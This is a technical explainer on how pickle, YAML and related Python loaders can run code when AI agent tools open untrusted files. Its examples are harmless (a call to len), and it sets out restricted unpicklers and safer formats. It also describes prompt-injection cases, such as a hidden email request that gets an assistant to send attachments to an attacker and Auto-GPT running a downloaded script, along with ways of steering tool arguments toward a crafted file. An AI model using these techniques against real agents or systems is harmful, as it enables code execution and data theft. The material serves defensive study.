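# Unsafe deserialization in AI agent tools: pickle, YAML and model code that runs on loading

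## How loading data can run code, and what an AI agent adds

Unsafe deserialization is a software flaw in which a program loads stored data into memory and, in doing so, runs code chosen by whoever created the data. The standard catalogue of software weaknesses has listed it since 2006. It matters for AI agents, which are programs that let a language model operate software tools, because developers write many of those tools in Python, and some of Python's most convenient ways of saving and loading data can run code in this way. Someone who gets such a tool to open a crafted file may be able to run their own code on the agent's machine, which security engineers call remote code execution.

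### One record, saved two ways

A running program keeps its values in memory, in a form that other programs cannot use. To store or send them, it must first turn them into bytes or text, which is called serialization. Deserialization rebuilds the values from the bytes or text, and a loader is any function that does this.

Take a weather reading of seven degrees in Oslo. In JSON, a text format that nearly every programming language can read, it looks like this:

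```json
{"city": "Oslo", "celsius": 7}
```

JSON is a data-only format: a loader can produce only text, numbers, true, false, null, lists, and tables of names and values. A stranger who writes the file can put a false temperature in it, but loading it still produces only those plain values or an error. According to the Python documentation's *pickle* page, loading untrusted JSON "does not in itself create an arbitrary code execution vulnerability". A malicious JSON string may still use up considerable processor time and memory, according to the documentation's *json* page, which recommends limiting the size of the input.

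Inside a Python program the same reading is often an object, which is a bundle of values attached to a class. The class is the code that defines what the program can do with them. Suppose this one sits in a file with the name `weather.py`:

```python
class Reading:
    def __init__(self, city, celsius):
        self.city = city
        self.celsius = celsius

    def fahrenheit(self):
        return self.celsius * 9 / 5 + 32
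```

Python's built-in format for saving such objects is pickle. A pickle of `Reading("Oslo", 7)` contains the two values, the module name `weather` and the class name `Reading`. The code of `fahrenheit` is not in it. Pickle stores classes and functions by name only, and Python's developers did this on purpose, so that a programmer can fix a bug in a class and still load objects from before the fix. The price is that the loader has to find the class and build an instance of it. By default it does roughly the following:

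```python
module = importlib.import_module("weather")  # name from the file
cls = getattr(module, "Reading")             # name from the file
obj = cls.__new__(cls)                       # an empty Reading
obj.__dict__.update({"city": "Oslo", "celsius": 7})
```

The JSON record needs none of this, since the loader can already create numbers and text. Two strings in the pickle file determine which module Python imports and what it takes from that module. Importing a module for the first time already runs the statements in it. If the class has a `__setstate__` method, the loader also calls that method with the saved values.

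Some objects cannot be restored by filling in their attributes, so pickle also lets a class specify a callable (anything Python can call, such as a function or a class) and the arguments to call it with. According to the Python documentation, the lookup step, `find_class`, returns functions as well as classes. A valid pickle can therefore name the built-in function `len` and give it the argument `"Oslo"`, and loading it calls `len("Oslo")` and returns 4. The format does not distinguish callables that are sensible for restoring data from those that are not, so if a pickle names a function that starts other programs instead of `len`, loading it starts a program.

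Loading a pickle file is the clearest example of how loading data can run code. Some YAML loaders build objects from tags in the text, and a model repository can include Python files that run when someone loads the model.

### The two conditions, and the category CWE-502

The flaw exists only when an outsider can influence the bytes and the loader turns names in those bytes into calls. A pickle is not a problem if the program wrote it itself to a disk that nobody else can write to. A JSON file from a stranger is not a problem either, as far as code execution goes.

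The standard category for the flaw is CWE-502, "Deserialization of Untrusted Data", in the Common Weakness Enumeration, a catalogue of software weaknesses that the US non-profit MITRE maintains. The entry defines it as a product deserializing untrusted data "without sufficiently ensuring that the resulting data will be valid". Besides loaders that run an attacker's code, this covers loaders that never finish or that let an attacker alter values the program treats as safe. The entry lists Java, Ruby, PHP, Python and JavaScript as languages where the weakness appears, and marks it as often prevalent in AI and machine-learning products, but gives no figure.

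Public databases probably record something over three thousand distinct unsafe deserialization flaws. GCVE's *CWE-502* page, part of a public vulnerability database, listed 6,035 entries in late October 2026, but that count is too high because the database also includes GitHub's security advisories, many of which repeat a vulnerability that already has a CVE identifier (the public number for a recorded vulnerability). The *CWE-502* page of cve.yack.one, a small third-party mirror that counts only CVE records, listed 3,219 in late summer. The lower count still includes flaws that don't let an outsider run code, such as one that let a malformed transaction crash a cryptocurrency node.

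Attackers use the weakness more than its overall rank would suggest. It ranked 15th in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 25 Most Dangerous Software Weaknesses*, up from 16th the year before. It ranked 5th in MITRE's *2025 CWE Top 10 KEV Weaknesses List Insights*, which applied the same scoring to 182 vulnerabilities from the US government's catalogue of flaws that attackers are known to have exploited. MITRE offers several possible reasons for such gaps, including that some weaknesses are easier to exploit and that attackers most want code execution. Both rankings cover all software and give no separate figure for agents.

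### How each condition arises, and what a list can do about it

Developers often misjudge who can control the data their programs load. The server of manga-image-translator, a tool for translating comics, unpickled the bodies of incoming requests. It had an authorization check based on a secret value, but the secret was empty by default, which made the server skip the check, according to the GCVE record. pyLoad, a download manager, unpickled its own session files, but users with certain permissions could redirect downloads into the folder that held those files, according to the cve.yack.one record.

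The Python documentation and MITRE both suggest signing data, since a signature can show that the bytes come from someone who holds a secret key. This prevents unsafe loading only if the signature is checked before the data is unpickled. In one of MITRE's faulty examples, a server unpickles an authentication token and then verifies the signature inside it, by which time any call in the pickle has already run. Checking that the loaded value has the right type comes too late for the same reason.

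The other approach is to stop names from becoming calls, and a data-only format does that completely. A developer who has to keep pickle can subclass its loader and override `find_class` to refuse some names. The override can use a denylist, which blocks the listed callables and lets everything else through, or an allowlist, which accepts only the listed callables. A denylist is unreliable because its author would have to think of every dangerous callable in the standard library and in every installed package, including future releases. A gap in an allowlist only stops a legitimate file from loading, which users notice and report.

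Allowlists fail in other ways, mostly by permitting too much. gpt_academic, an academic-writing application that runs on language models, used an allowlist for its pickles that included numpy, a large numerical library. Attackers could use numpy to run commands, according to the CVE-2024-11039 record in CIRCL's *CWE-502* listing. OpenAM, a Java login server, applied an allowlist to one request parameter but left another that reached an unprotected loader, as cve.yack.one records. MITRE recommends allowlists but does not consider them sufficient alone, because researchers keep discovering new "gadgets", which are pieces of code already present in ordinary libraries that do damage when a loader triggers them.

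### Where outsiders' data enters an agent

An agent works in a loop. Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize a supplier's published measurements, and the agent has a tool function `load_table(path)`.

1. The language model reads text. This includes the user's request, the developer's instructions and descriptions of the tools, along with any web pages, emails or documents that earlier rounds fetched. **Outsiders' text enters here.**
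2. The model chooses a tool, in this case `load_table`.
3. The model writes the arguments, such as the path `downloads/results.pkl`. Anything it read in step 1 can affect what it writes.
4. The host process, meaning the program that runs the agent and holds its credentials, calls the tool with those arguments. The tool opens the file. **Outsiders' bytes enter here**, without passing through the model.
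5. The host process adds the result to the model's text, and the loop starts again. If a stranger wrote the file, **the stranger's words are now part of step 1**.

A model receives both its instructions and the material it works on as text, and does not reliably tell them apart. In prompt injection, someone exploits this by planting text in a page, file or message that the model takes as an instruction. Sotiropoulos (2026), in *Agentic Security*, gives the example of an email containing a hidden request. When the user later asks an assistant to summarize the thread, the assistant sends earlier messages and attachments to the attacker. Sotiropoulos co-leads the agent-risk list of the Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes rankings of security risks. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026)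 reports that in August 2026 OWASP put prompt injection first on its list for language-model applications for the third year running, even though recorded incidents are relatively few.

With `load_table`, an attacker might only need to put a sentence on the supplier's page saying that the full results are in a particular file. Often even that is unnecessary. If the user asks the agent to open a malicious attachment, the model calls the loader as requested, and the loader runs the attacker's code. Step 4 is ordinary Python, so once the loader has started on a pickle, neither the model's caution nor an instruction to avoid dangerous files has any effect.

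### What the agent changes

In a conventional program, a developer usually decides which file a loader opens, or at least which part of the program chooses it. In an agent, the model fills in the argument at run time. Sotiropoulos notes, under tool misuse, that attackers can use injected content to influence both the choice of tool and its arguments. Anyone whose text the model reads can therefore influence a parameter that the tool's author thought of as internal, such as the path to a cache file. It is sensible to trust a tool's arguments no more than the contents of a web form. OWASP calls neglecting this improper output handling and lists remote code execution among its results. SC Media's *OWASP updates top 10 security risks for LLM applications* reports that it is last of the ten entries in the 2026 list. That list ranks risks for language-model applications in general, and a tool that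 passes a path to a pickle loader deserves more concern than tenth place implies.

An agent also increases the damage that unsafe loading can do, because code that runs inside the host process can use whatever that process can use, which may include keys for email, source code or cloud accounts. Sotiropoulos describes agents reusing credentials from memory or tool responses and carrying them across tasks, so that a high-privilege GitHub token ends up in an agent that should never have had it. A flaw in a minor file-reading tool can therefore expose far more than the tool needs.

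The loader works the same way with or without an AI agent. The Python 3.1 documentation, from 2009, included a warning never to unpickle data from an untrusted source, and MITRE's references include articles on pickle's insecurity from 2009 and 2011. New cases that don't involve AI keep appearing. In 2026, the courseware package RELATE was found to accept pickles from its internal message queue, which let a logged-in student take over the host server, according to GCVE. Software for building agents can also have the flaw in its original form. IBM's Langflow Desktop, a visual agent builder, had an insecure default setting that permitted unsafe loading in its component for the search library FAISS. The attacker in the cve.yack.one record is a user with an account, and the attack doesn't involve prompt injection.

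### Agents that are meant to run code, and OWASP's classification

Some agents, such as the early open-source agent Auto-GPT, are designed to run code. Sotiropoulos recounts a demonstration by the firm Positive Security in which Auto-GPT browsed a page containing an instruction to download and run a script. It ran the script inside a container, and the attacker's commands then escaped to the host through misconfigurations. The attack used a feature that was working as designed. People who install such a feature know that it executes code, so they can isolate it or require approval for each command. Nothing indicates that `load_table` can also run code, so a user who approves "read results.pkl" approves a set of function calls without seeing them.

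If an agent has a command-line tool with the same privileges as its loader, an attacker who can steer the model gains little from a malicious pickle. The pickle still helps an attacker who can supply a file but cannot steer the model. It also helps a great deal when the command-line tool runs in a sandbox but the loader runs in the host process.

OWASP puts both kinds of case under one heading, Unexpected Code Execution (ASI05). It is the fifth entry in the Top 10 for Agentic Applications, published in December 2025 (OWASP, 2025). According to Sotiropoulos's slides, an attacker who manipulates an agent's prompts or other input can cause it through generated code, shell commands or "agent deserialization". The summary slide is marked as a release candidate, but Palo Alto Networks' *OWASP Agentic AI Top 10 Survival Guide*, a security vendor's commentary on the published list, has almost the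 same wording, so deserialization seems to have stayed in. Deserialization gets little attention in the slides, though, and the one that explains ASI05 is about agents generating and running scripts, with Auto-GPT as its example.

Other entries overlap with ASI05. A crafted model file from an unverified source is also a supply-chain problem (ASI04), and if the code in it uses the agent's tokens, ASI03, on identity and privilege, applies as well. OWASP's older list for web applications similarly merged insecure deserialization, which had its own entry in 2017, into a wider category on software and data integrity by 2021, according to the memberships in MITRE's entry. In a review, ASI05 describes the outcome well enough, but it fits a badly isolated shell tool equally well. CWE-502 identifies the flaw as unsafe deserialization, so a developer knows to look for the line that calls the loader.

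## Reading what a pickle will do before it is loaded

After finding a line that calls a pickle loader, a reviewer needs to know what a particular file would make that loader do. Python's pickletools module prints the steps in a pickle as text without loading the file. Someone who recognizes roughly five kinds of step can usually tell which functions the file would call and with what arguments.

### The pickle machine

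A pickle is a program in a very small language. It consists of one-byte instructions called opcodes, some of which are followed by a number or a piece of text. The loader carries out each opcode once, in order, until it reaches STOP. The language has no loops, conditions or arithmetic, according to the comments in the pickletools source code.

The loader keeps its values on a stack, and opcodes add values to the top or remove them. It also has a memo, a numbered store for values that the pickle needs more than once. When the loader reaches the STOP opcode, it returns the value on top of the stack.

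This is the listing for `Reading("Oslo", 7)`, the weather reading from the previous section. `pickletools.optimize` has shortened it by removing the opcodes that write memo entries that are never read.

```
    0: \x80 PROTO      5
    2: \x95 FRAME      49
   11: \x8c SHORT_BINUNICODE 'weather'
   20: \x8c SHORT_BINUNICODE 'Reading'
   29: \x93 STACK_GLOBAL
   30: )    EMPTY_TUPLE
   31: \x81 NEWOBJ
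   32: }    EMPTY_DICT
   33: (    MARK
   34: \x8c     SHORT_BINUNICODE 'city'
   40: \x8c     SHORT_BINUNICODE 'Oslo'
   46: \x8c     SHORT_BINUNICODE 'celsius'
   55: K        BININT1    7
   57: u        SETITEMS   (MARK at 33)
   58: b    BUILD
   59: .    STOP
highest protocol among opcodes = 4
```

Each line shows an opcode's position in the file, its byte, its name and its argument. PROTO gives the version of the format (5 is the default since Python 3.14), and FRAME gives the length of the next block of bytes. The two text opcodes then put `'weather'` and `'Reading'` on the stack. STACK_GLOBAL takes both off, imports the module and puts the class in their place. NEWOBJ creates an empty instance. The next opcodes assemble a dictionary of attributes, and BUILD copies it into the instance.

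Most opcodes only handle plain values such as text, numbers and lists. These are the ones that matter most for security:

| Opcode | What it uses | What the loader does |
|---|---|---|
| GLOBAL | A module name and an object name, which follow the opcode in the file | Imports the module and puts the named object on the stack |
| STACK_GLOBAL | The same two names, taken from the stack | The same |
| REDUCE | A callable and a tuple of arguments | Calls the callable and puts the result on the stack |
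| NEWOBJ | A class and a tuple of arguments | Calls the class's `__new__` method and puts the new instance on the stack |
| BUILD | An object and its saved state | Calls the object's `__setstate__` method or, if there is none, fills in its attributes |

The REDUCE opcode calls any Python callable that an earlier opcode has put on the stack. The source comments also describe the pickle language as having no function calls, which is true only in the sense that a pickle cannot define a function in its own opcodes.

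A lookup can have effects even without REDUCE, because it imports the module that contains the name, and a module's statements run when it is first imported. As a harmless example, the standard library's `this` module prints a short poem about Python's design on first import, so loading a pickle that only looks up the name `s` in `this` can print the poem.

### What `__reduce__` writes, and what the loader calls

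When filling in attributes is not enough to rebuild an object, its class can define a `__reduce__` method that specifies a callable and its arguments for doing so. Pickle calls this method when it saves the object. The method can return a string, which pickle treats as the name of an existing object, but it usually returns a tuple of the callable and its arguments. *PICKLEBALL* (Kellas, Li et al., 2025) gives a typical example of a class for numerical data whose `__reduce__` returns a function that reads weights from a file, together with the filename.

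According to the Python documentation, the tuple can have up to four more items: the object's state, items to append if the object is a kind of list, pairs to add if it is a kind of dictionary, and a second callable that sets the state. Pickle writes the call to this second callable as another REDUCE, so restoring one object can involve two calls.

The following class produces the `len("Oslo")` call from the previous section:

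```python
import pickle, pickletools

class CityName:
    def __init__(self, city):
        self.city = city

    def __reduce__(self):
        return (len, (self.city,))

data = pickle.dumps(CityName("Oslo"))
pickletools.dis(pickletools.optimize(data))
```

When `dumps` saves the object, it calls `__reduce__` and gets back the function `len` and the tuple `("Oslo",)`. It writes the function as a module name and a function name, then the arguments, then REDUCE:

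```
    0: \x80 PROTO      5
    2: \x95 FRAME      25
   11: \x8c SHORT_BINUNICODE 'builtins'
   21: \x8c SHORT_BINUNICODE 'len'
   26: \x93 STACK_GLOBAL
   27: \x8c SHORT_BINUNICODE 'Oslo'
   33: \x85 TUPLE1
   34: R    REDUCE
   35: .    STOP
highest protocol among opcodes = 4
```

On loading, the stack changes as follows, with the top of the stack on the right:

| After the opcode at | Stack |
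|---|---|
| 11, text | `'builtins'` |
| 21, text | `'builtins'`, `'len'` |
| 26, STACK_GLOBAL | the function `len` |
| 27, text | the function `len`, `'Oslo'` |
| 33, TUPLE1 | the function `len`, `('Oslo',)` |
| 34, REDUCE | `4` |
| 35, STOP | empty; the loader returns `4` |

Neither `CityName` nor `__reduce__` appears in the file. A program with no `CityName` class will still get 4 from `pickle.loads(data)`. The pickle of `Reading`, by contrast, fails to load wherever Python cannot import `weather`.

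An outsider can write a pickle that makes a call when loaded without knowing anything about the classes in an agent's tools. The pickle only has to name a callable that the agent's Python installation can import, and the built-in functions and standard library are available almost everywhere. The outsider doesn't need to define a class either. The Python documentation includes a short pickle, written by hand as a byte string, that makes a call in the same way.

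### Listing a file without running it

The same listing is available from the command line:

```
python -m pickletools results.pkl
```

The command `python -m pickle results.pkl` loads the file to display the stored object. For files from an untrusted source, the Python documentation's *pickletools* page recommends `python -m pickletools` instead because it does not execute the pickle.

In the listing, a reviewer should find the module and name for every GLOBAL and STACK_GLOBAL. For STACK_GLOBAL, these are usually the two strings just before it, but either may come from the memo. The reviewer should also check some rarer opcodes. INST and OBJ are old ways of creating instances, NEWOBJ_EX is a variant of NEWOBJ, and the EXT opcodes fetch objects from a registry. Current versions of Python still accept the old opcodes because pickle opcodes are never removed.

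Whether a REDUCE opcode indicates an attack depends on the callable and its arguments. In the oldest version of the format, even the harmless bytes value `b'abc'` produces a REDUCE, which calls Python's own text-encoding function.

A pickle with no lookups at all is much simpler to judge. This function checks for them:

```python
LOOKUPS = {"GLOBAL", "STACK_GLOBAL", "INST",
           "EXT1", "EXT2", "EXT4"}

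def has_lookup(data):
    return any(op.name in LOOKUPS
               for op, arg, pos in pickletools.genops(data))
```

If the result is `False`, an ordinary loader can get only plain values out of the pickle, because REDUCE and NEWOBJ have nothing to call. (A program that defines its own `persistent_load` method, for references to objects outside the pickle, needs a separate look at that method.)

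A pickletools listing ends at the first STOP opcode. Some files contain several pickles in a row, and a program that calls the loader repeatedly on the same open file will load each in turn, so a reviewer has to list them all. A pickle can also contain another pickle as a bytes value, which pickletools prints as bytes without disassembling it.

A post on the AWS Security Blog is more pessimistic about inspection, stating that nobody can thoroughly evaluate the data in a pickle before unpickling it. This is true of the pickle's effects, because a listing names a function but doesn't show what it does, and a reviewer may have to read the source of an unfamiliar library to find out. But the listing is still enough to reject many files. If a pickled table of measurements looks up a function for starting programs, a reviewer can reject it without working out the details.

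Loading the file to see whether an error comes up is not safe. The loader executes the opcodes in order, so it can make several calls before it reaches the damaged part of a pickle.

### Why a check on the loaded value comes too late

A type check after loading has the same problem. MONAI, an open-source toolkit for AI in medical imaging, had one in `algo_from_pickle`, a function that restores a saved training algorithm. The file holds a pickled dictionary, and one value in it, `algo_bytes`, is a second pickle with the algorithm inside. In simplified form, the function did this:

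```python
data = pickle.loads(raw)        # calls in the outer pickle happen here
if not isinstance(data, dict):
    raise ValueError("expected a dictionary")
if "algo_bytes" not in data:
    raise ValueError("no algorithm in the file")
algo = pickle.loads(data["algo_bytes"])  # calls in the inner pickle
```

Both checks help catch honest mistakes, such as opening the wrong file. Neither can prevent a call in the outer pickle, because that call runs before the checks do. A malicious file can also pass both checks. If someone pickles `{"city": CityName("Oslo")}`, loading it calls `len` and returns `{"city": 4}`, which is a valid dictionary.

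Between the two loads, the function also added folders to Python's module search path. It took one of them from the file's `template_path` value, if that folder existed. The file could therefore influence both which names the loader looked up and which code a module name referred to.

GitLab's *GHSA-89gg-p5r5-q6r4*, an advisory dated 7 April 2026, describes the flaw and lists MONAI 1.5.2 as the release that fixed it. A later advisory, which the security company Kodem reproduces in *GHSA-QXQ5-QHX6-94QW*, reports that nobody had fixed it. The source file had not changed since 12 July 2024, about 18 months before 1.5.2 came out, and still contained all three calls to `pickle.loads` (the inner load appears twice, in different branches). The first advisory had mistakenly cited the fix for an unrelated flaw in unpacking archives, according to SecureLayer7's *MONAI algo_from_pickle() Unsafe Pickle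 Deserialization RCE (Incomplete Fix)*.

Version 1.5.2 still contained `pickle.loads`, though anyone who followed the first advisory and upgraded to it would have had good reason to think the problem was gone. Searching the installed package for `pickle.loads` would have found it in a few seconds, and is worth doing after any upgrade that is supposed to remove unsafe loading.

The flaw has a severity score of 7.8 out of 10. The score isn't higher partly because the attack needs local access and some action by a user. In an agent, the model can take that action itself by opening a file.

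The real fix came in version 1.6.0 of MONAI (2026), dated 11 June. The saving and loading functions now raise an error unless someone sets the environment variable `MONAI_ALLOW_PICKLE=1`, and they give a warning even then. MONAI saves these algorithms as JSON instead, which its *What’s new in 1.6.0* describes as removing a class of security risks.

That is an improvement, but the new loader isn't data-only in the sense used here. According to MONAI's *Auto3dseg* documentation, it reads a full class name from the file, creates an instance of that class and restores its state. The documentation mentions no list of permitted classes. Anyone who passes files from outsiders to `algo_from_json` should check which class names it accepts.

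### Letting the loader find only certain names

To prevent a call, a restriction has to act during loading, as an override of `find_class` does. The loader uses that method for every GLOBAL and STACK_GLOBAL. A program that needs to load only `Reading` objects can override it like this:

```python
import io, pickle
from weather import Reading

ALLOWED = {("weather", "Reading"): Reading}

class ReadingUnpickler(pickle.Unpickler):
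    def find_class(self, module, name):
        if (module, name) not in ALLOWED:
            raise pickle.UnpicklingError(
                f"{module}.{name} is not allowed")
        return ALLOWED[module, name]

def load_reading(data):
    return ReadingUnpickler(io.BytesIO(data)).load()
```

With the `CityName` pickle, `load_reading` fails at byte 26, where STACK_GLOBAL refers to `builtins.len`, so the loader never reaches REDUCE. The override never imports a module named in the file, because it returns a class that the program has already imported. If `ALLOWED` is empty, the loader accepts only plain values.

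A developer can draw up the list by loading files from a trusted source and recording the names those files need. Each time Python's own `find_class` is called, it raises an auditing event with the module and name, which a program can log.

The dictionary matches the module and the name together, which is safer than matching the module alone. From protocol 4 onward, Python's default `find_class` follows dots within a name. If `weather.py` imports `math`, the name `math.sqrt` in the module `weather` resolves to the square-root function. An override that checks only that the module is `weather` and then calls the default method therefore also allows anything `weather` has imported.

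Even an exact allowlist controls only which callables a pickle can use, and the sender still chooses the arguments and the saved state. For example, the Python documentation includes a class, `TextReader`, that saves its place in a text file. Its `__setstate__` method reopens the file named in the saved state. A developer might reasonably allow `TextReader`, but a stranger's pickle could then make the program open any file it has permission to read. The same would be true of the weight-reading function in the example by Kellas and colleagues.

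Plain classes can cause trouble too, because BUILD normally fills in attributes without running `__init__`. Even if `Reading.__init__` checked that the temperature was a number, a pickle could produce a `Reading` whose temperature was a string. It could also set an attribute named `fahrenheit` to a number, which would hide the method of that name on the loaded object. Code that uses such objects has to validate them after loading.

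Python itself once had a restriction of this kind. Up to version 2.2, REDUCE called a function only if a developer had marked it as safe. Python's developers removed the checks in version 2.3. According to comments in Android's copy of the source, nobody had done enough security analysis to guarantee that untrusted pickles were safe to load, and no use of pickle justified the work. The description of REDUCE later in the file still mentions the old checks, which could mislead someone who reads only that part.

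The Python documentation's pickle page now begins with the warning "The pickle module is not secure. Only unpickle data you trust." It presents `find_class` as a way of "potentially reducing security risks" and suggests other formats where security is a concern. *Never a dill moment* (2021), an article by the security firm Trail of Bits, goes further and says that attackers can almost always get around protections for loading pickles.

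That is probably too pessimistic about an allowlist of one or two simple classes, since a developer can read all the code it exposes. It is fair for denylists and for allowlists that admit whole libraries, like the one in gpt_academic. Whether it is fair for allowlists between these extremes depends on what the permitted code does. Kellas and colleagues, whose PickleBall tool works out an allowlist for each machine-learning library, acknowledge that attackers can still try to misuse the permitted code.

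But a program that needs only one or two simple classes rarely needs pickle. If the file contains the JSON record from the previous section, `Reading(**json.loads(text))` creates the same object. The class name is then in the program rather than the file, and `__init__` runs with any checks it contains. A restricted unpickler is most useful for old files that nobody can convert yet.

### Other functions that load pickles

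Many tools use pickle without the word appearing in their code. The Python documentation gives the example of `shelve`, a standard library module that works like a dictionary stored on disk. SecureLayer7 lists related flaws in `read_webdataset`, a function in the distributed-computing library Ray that uses a pickle decoder by default, and in BabelDOC, a PDF translator, through its character-map files. PyTorch's `torch.load`, which loads weights files, also reads pickles but has restricted them by default since version 2.6.

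The libraries in this table are common in Python data work, so they are likely to turn up in an agent's tools:

| Loader | Default behaviour | Data-only replacement |
|---|---|---|
| `cloudpickle.load` | Loads any pickle | JSON with the name of a task that the receiver already has, and its arguments |
| `dill.load` | Loads any pickle | JSON for the values, with functions and classes kept in installed code |
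| `joblib.load` | Loads any pickle | NumPy's `.npy` format for arrays, JSON for settings |
| `pandas.read_pickle` | Loads any pickle, from a path or a web address | CSV or Parquet |
| `numpy.load` | Refuses pickles unless the caller passes `allow_pickle=True` | `.npy` or `.npz` with the default setting |
| `jsonpickle.decode` | Looks up classes and functions that the JSON names | `json.loads`, after which the program creates its own objects |

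cloudpickle and dill can save things that ordinary pickle cannot, such as functions typed into a notebook, by putting the function's compiled code in the file. `cloudpickle.load` is `pickle.load` under another name, so loading the file with ordinary pickle is just as dangerous. An allowlist offers little protection, because one that permits everything these files need also permits code written by the sender. According to cloudpickle's page on PyPI, Python's package index, the library is meant for sending code between computers in a cluster, works only between identical versions of Python, and is unsuitable for long-term storage. A tool that opens cloudpickle files from outside is therefore using the library for something it was not designed to do.

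**joblib** is a common way to save models from the machine-learning library scikit-learn. Calmcode's *scikit save*, a tutorial, illustrates the risk with a fake model whose `predict` method prints a message. That file would not load in a program without the fake class, because joblib, like pickle, stores the class by name. A file that contains a REDUCE has no such limitation, and its call runs on loading, before anyone asks for a prediction. joblib's caching feature, `joblib.Memory`, also loads pickles from its cache folder, so anyone who can write to that folder can run code. There is no good data-only format for an arbitrary scikit-learn model. The skops library comes closest for many of them, but it relies on an allowlist of trusted types.

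`pandas.read_pickle` needs particular care in an agent because it accepts web addresses as well as file paths. If a tool passes the model's argument straight to this function, an attacker doesn't have to get a file onto the machine first. Parquet, a format for tables, is a good replacement, but only with an up-to-date reader. PyArrow, the library pandas usually uses to read Parquet, could unpickle data from a crafted file until version 14.0.1 fixed this in 2023.

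**NumPy** has refused to load pickles by default since version 1.16.3, released in 2019. Ordinary numerical arrays don't need pickle, but `numpy.save` still uses it for arrays of arbitrary Python objects. It does so without a warning, so a developer may first learn of the problem when the file fails to load. Adding `allow_pickle=True` lets the file load but brings back the whole risk. Kodem's *GHSA-WG9G-W2J2-8PGR* reports that MONAI's image reader had this setting permanently on, so a crafted `.npy` image file could run code. MONAI 1.6.0 made it an option that is off by default. A tool that needs both text and numbers can avoid the problem by storing them in separate arrays with ordinary types.

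**jsonpickle** doesn't use the pickle format, but it has much the same power. Its files are valid JSON, and a `Reading` looks like this:

```json
{"py/object": "weather.Reading", "city": "Oslo", "celsius": 7}
```

`json.loads` reads this as a dictionary with three string keys. `jsonpickle.decode` treats `py/object` as an instruction to import `weather` and create a `Reading`, and it also makes the calls that `__reduce__` specifies. Its `safe` option, on by default since version 4, only turns off an old feature that evaluated text as Python code. It doesn't stop these imports and calls, so a reviewer who sees a `.json` file still has to check which function opens it.

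## Parsing YAML without building objects or calling functions

jsonpickle can turn ordinary-looking JSON into function calls, and some YAML loaders do the same with YAML. YAML is a text format that many people find easier to write by hand than JSON, and agent frameworks often use it for settings, workflows and definitions of agents. A weather reading looks like this:

```yaml
city: Oslo
country: NO
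celsius: 7
```

Whether opening such a file can run code depends on the loader and on what the program then does with the values.

### How a tag selects a constructor

A YAML tag gives the type of a value. The tag is written out in `celsius: !!int 7`, but if the line is just `celsius: 7`, the parser supplies the same tag because the value looks like a whole number. The `!!` is short for a longer prefix, so the full tag is `tag:yaml.org,2002:int`.

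PyYAML, the usual YAML library for Python, loads a file in three steps:

1. The parser turns the text into a tree, in which each node is a piece of text, a list or a table of names and values.
2. The resolver gives a tag to every node that lacks one.
3. The constructor looks up each node's tag in a table and runs the Python function it finds there.

Each loader has its own table that matches tags to functions. The function for `!!int` converts text to a number. Some tables also have entries for tag prefixes, whose functions treat the rest of the tag as a name. For the tag `!!python/object/apply:builtins.len`, the function looks up `builtins.len` and calls it. This tag is as powerful as the REDUCE opcode in a pickle, and PyYAML's `dump` function writes it for objects whose `__reduce__` method specifies a call.

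Developers can add their own entries with `add_constructor`. If a program adds one to SafeLoader, the strictest loader in common use, a file can trigger the function in that entry too. The addition affects all code in the same process that uses SafeLoader, including other libraries, so it is better to add the entry to a subclass. A reviewer who finds SafeLoader in a tool should also search for `add_constructor` and `add_multi_constructor`.

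### What four PyYAML loaders build

This harmless document has two values without tags and three with Python-specific tags:

```yaml
country: NO
celsius: 7
position: !!python/tuple [59.9, 10.7]
measure: !!python/name:builtins.len
length: !!python/object/apply:builtins.len [Oslo]
```

An error in one value makes a loader reject the whole document, so the table shows what PyYAML 6.0.3 does with each value separately:

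| Entry | BaseLoader | SafeLoader | FullLoader | UnsafeLoader |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `country` | `'NO'` | `False` | `False` | `False` |
| `celsius` | `'7'` | `7` | `7` | `7` |
| `position` | `['59.9', '10.7']` | Error | `(59.9, 10.7)` | `(59.9, 10.7)` |
| `measure` | `''` | Error | The function `len` | The function `len` |
| `length` | `['Oslo']` | Error | Error | `4` |

**BaseLoader** ignores the tags and produces only text, lists and dictionaries. The program then has to convert the numbers itself.

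`SafeLoader` produces the same plain values as a JSON loader, along with dates, sets and bytes. It rejects all three Python tags. It also reads `NO` as `False`, a well-known nuisance, because PyYAML follows older YAML rules that treat `yes`, `no`, `on` and `off` as booleans. Quoting the country code avoids this.

**FullLoader** can also build some Python types, such as tuples, and can return a function or class from a module that the program has already imported. It doesn't call the function, but a program that expects text may do so later, for example by passing the function to a library that accepts callbacks.

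**UnsafeLoader** imports whatever module a tag names and calls what it finds there.

`yaml.Loader` is as powerful as `UnsafeLoader`, despite its neutral name. The shortcuts `safe_load`, `full_load` and `unsafe_load` use `SafeLoader`, `FullLoader` and `UnsafeLoader` respectively.

### How PyYAML's defaults changed

For years, `yaml.load(text)` used the unrestricted loader unless the developer chose another, a default identified as CVE-2017-18342. Safety, a vulnerability database, lists versions before 4 as affected, but PyYAML's *CHANGES* file goes straight from 3.13 to 5.1, so a developer should treat every version before 5.1 as having the unsafe default.

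The changelog dates the later steps as follows:

| Version | Date | Change |
|---|---|---|
| 5.1 | 13 March 2019 | Deprecates `yaml.load` without a chosen loader, and adds FullLoader and UnsafeLoader |
| 5.2 | 2 December 2019 | Removes `python/object/apply` from FullLoader |
| 5.3.1 | 18 March 2020 | Blocks code execution through `python/object/new` |
| 5.4 | 19 January 2021 | Moves the tags that build arbitrary Python objects to UnsafeLoader |
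| 6.0 | 13 October 2021 | Makes the `Loader` argument compulsory in `yaml.load` |

From PyYAML 5.1, a plain `yaml.load(text)` gave a warning and used FullLoader. PyYAML's developers meant this as a safer default, but they took three more releases to achieve that. The CVE-2019-20477 entry on releasealert.dev's *yaml/pyyaml* page describes the restrictions in 5.1 to 5.1.2 as insufficient, and version 5.2 tightened them.

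The changelog gives no CVE number for the fix in 5.3.1, but the release notes, which GitHub reproduces, identify the flaw as CVE-2020-1747. They state that FullLoader "was still exploitable for arbitrary command execution" and credit Riccardo Schirone with both the report and the fix. The fix was a denylist that refused certain attribute names in the file, and it was incomplete. The remaining flaw is CVE-2020-14343.

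Version 5.4 took the more reliable approach of removing the `python/module`, `python/object` and `python/object/new` tags. Files that use them now need UnsafeLoader or a custom loader that enables them (Matt D., 2021, *Announcing PyYAML-5.4*). PyYAML lists no further security fixes up to version 6.0.3, released in September 2025.

Since PyYAML 6.0, calling `yaml.load` without a `Loader` argument raises an error. A developer in a hurry may fix the error by writing `Loader=yaml.Loader`, which brings back the behaviour from before 5.1. `Loader=yaml.SafeLoader` is the right choice for almost every configuration file.

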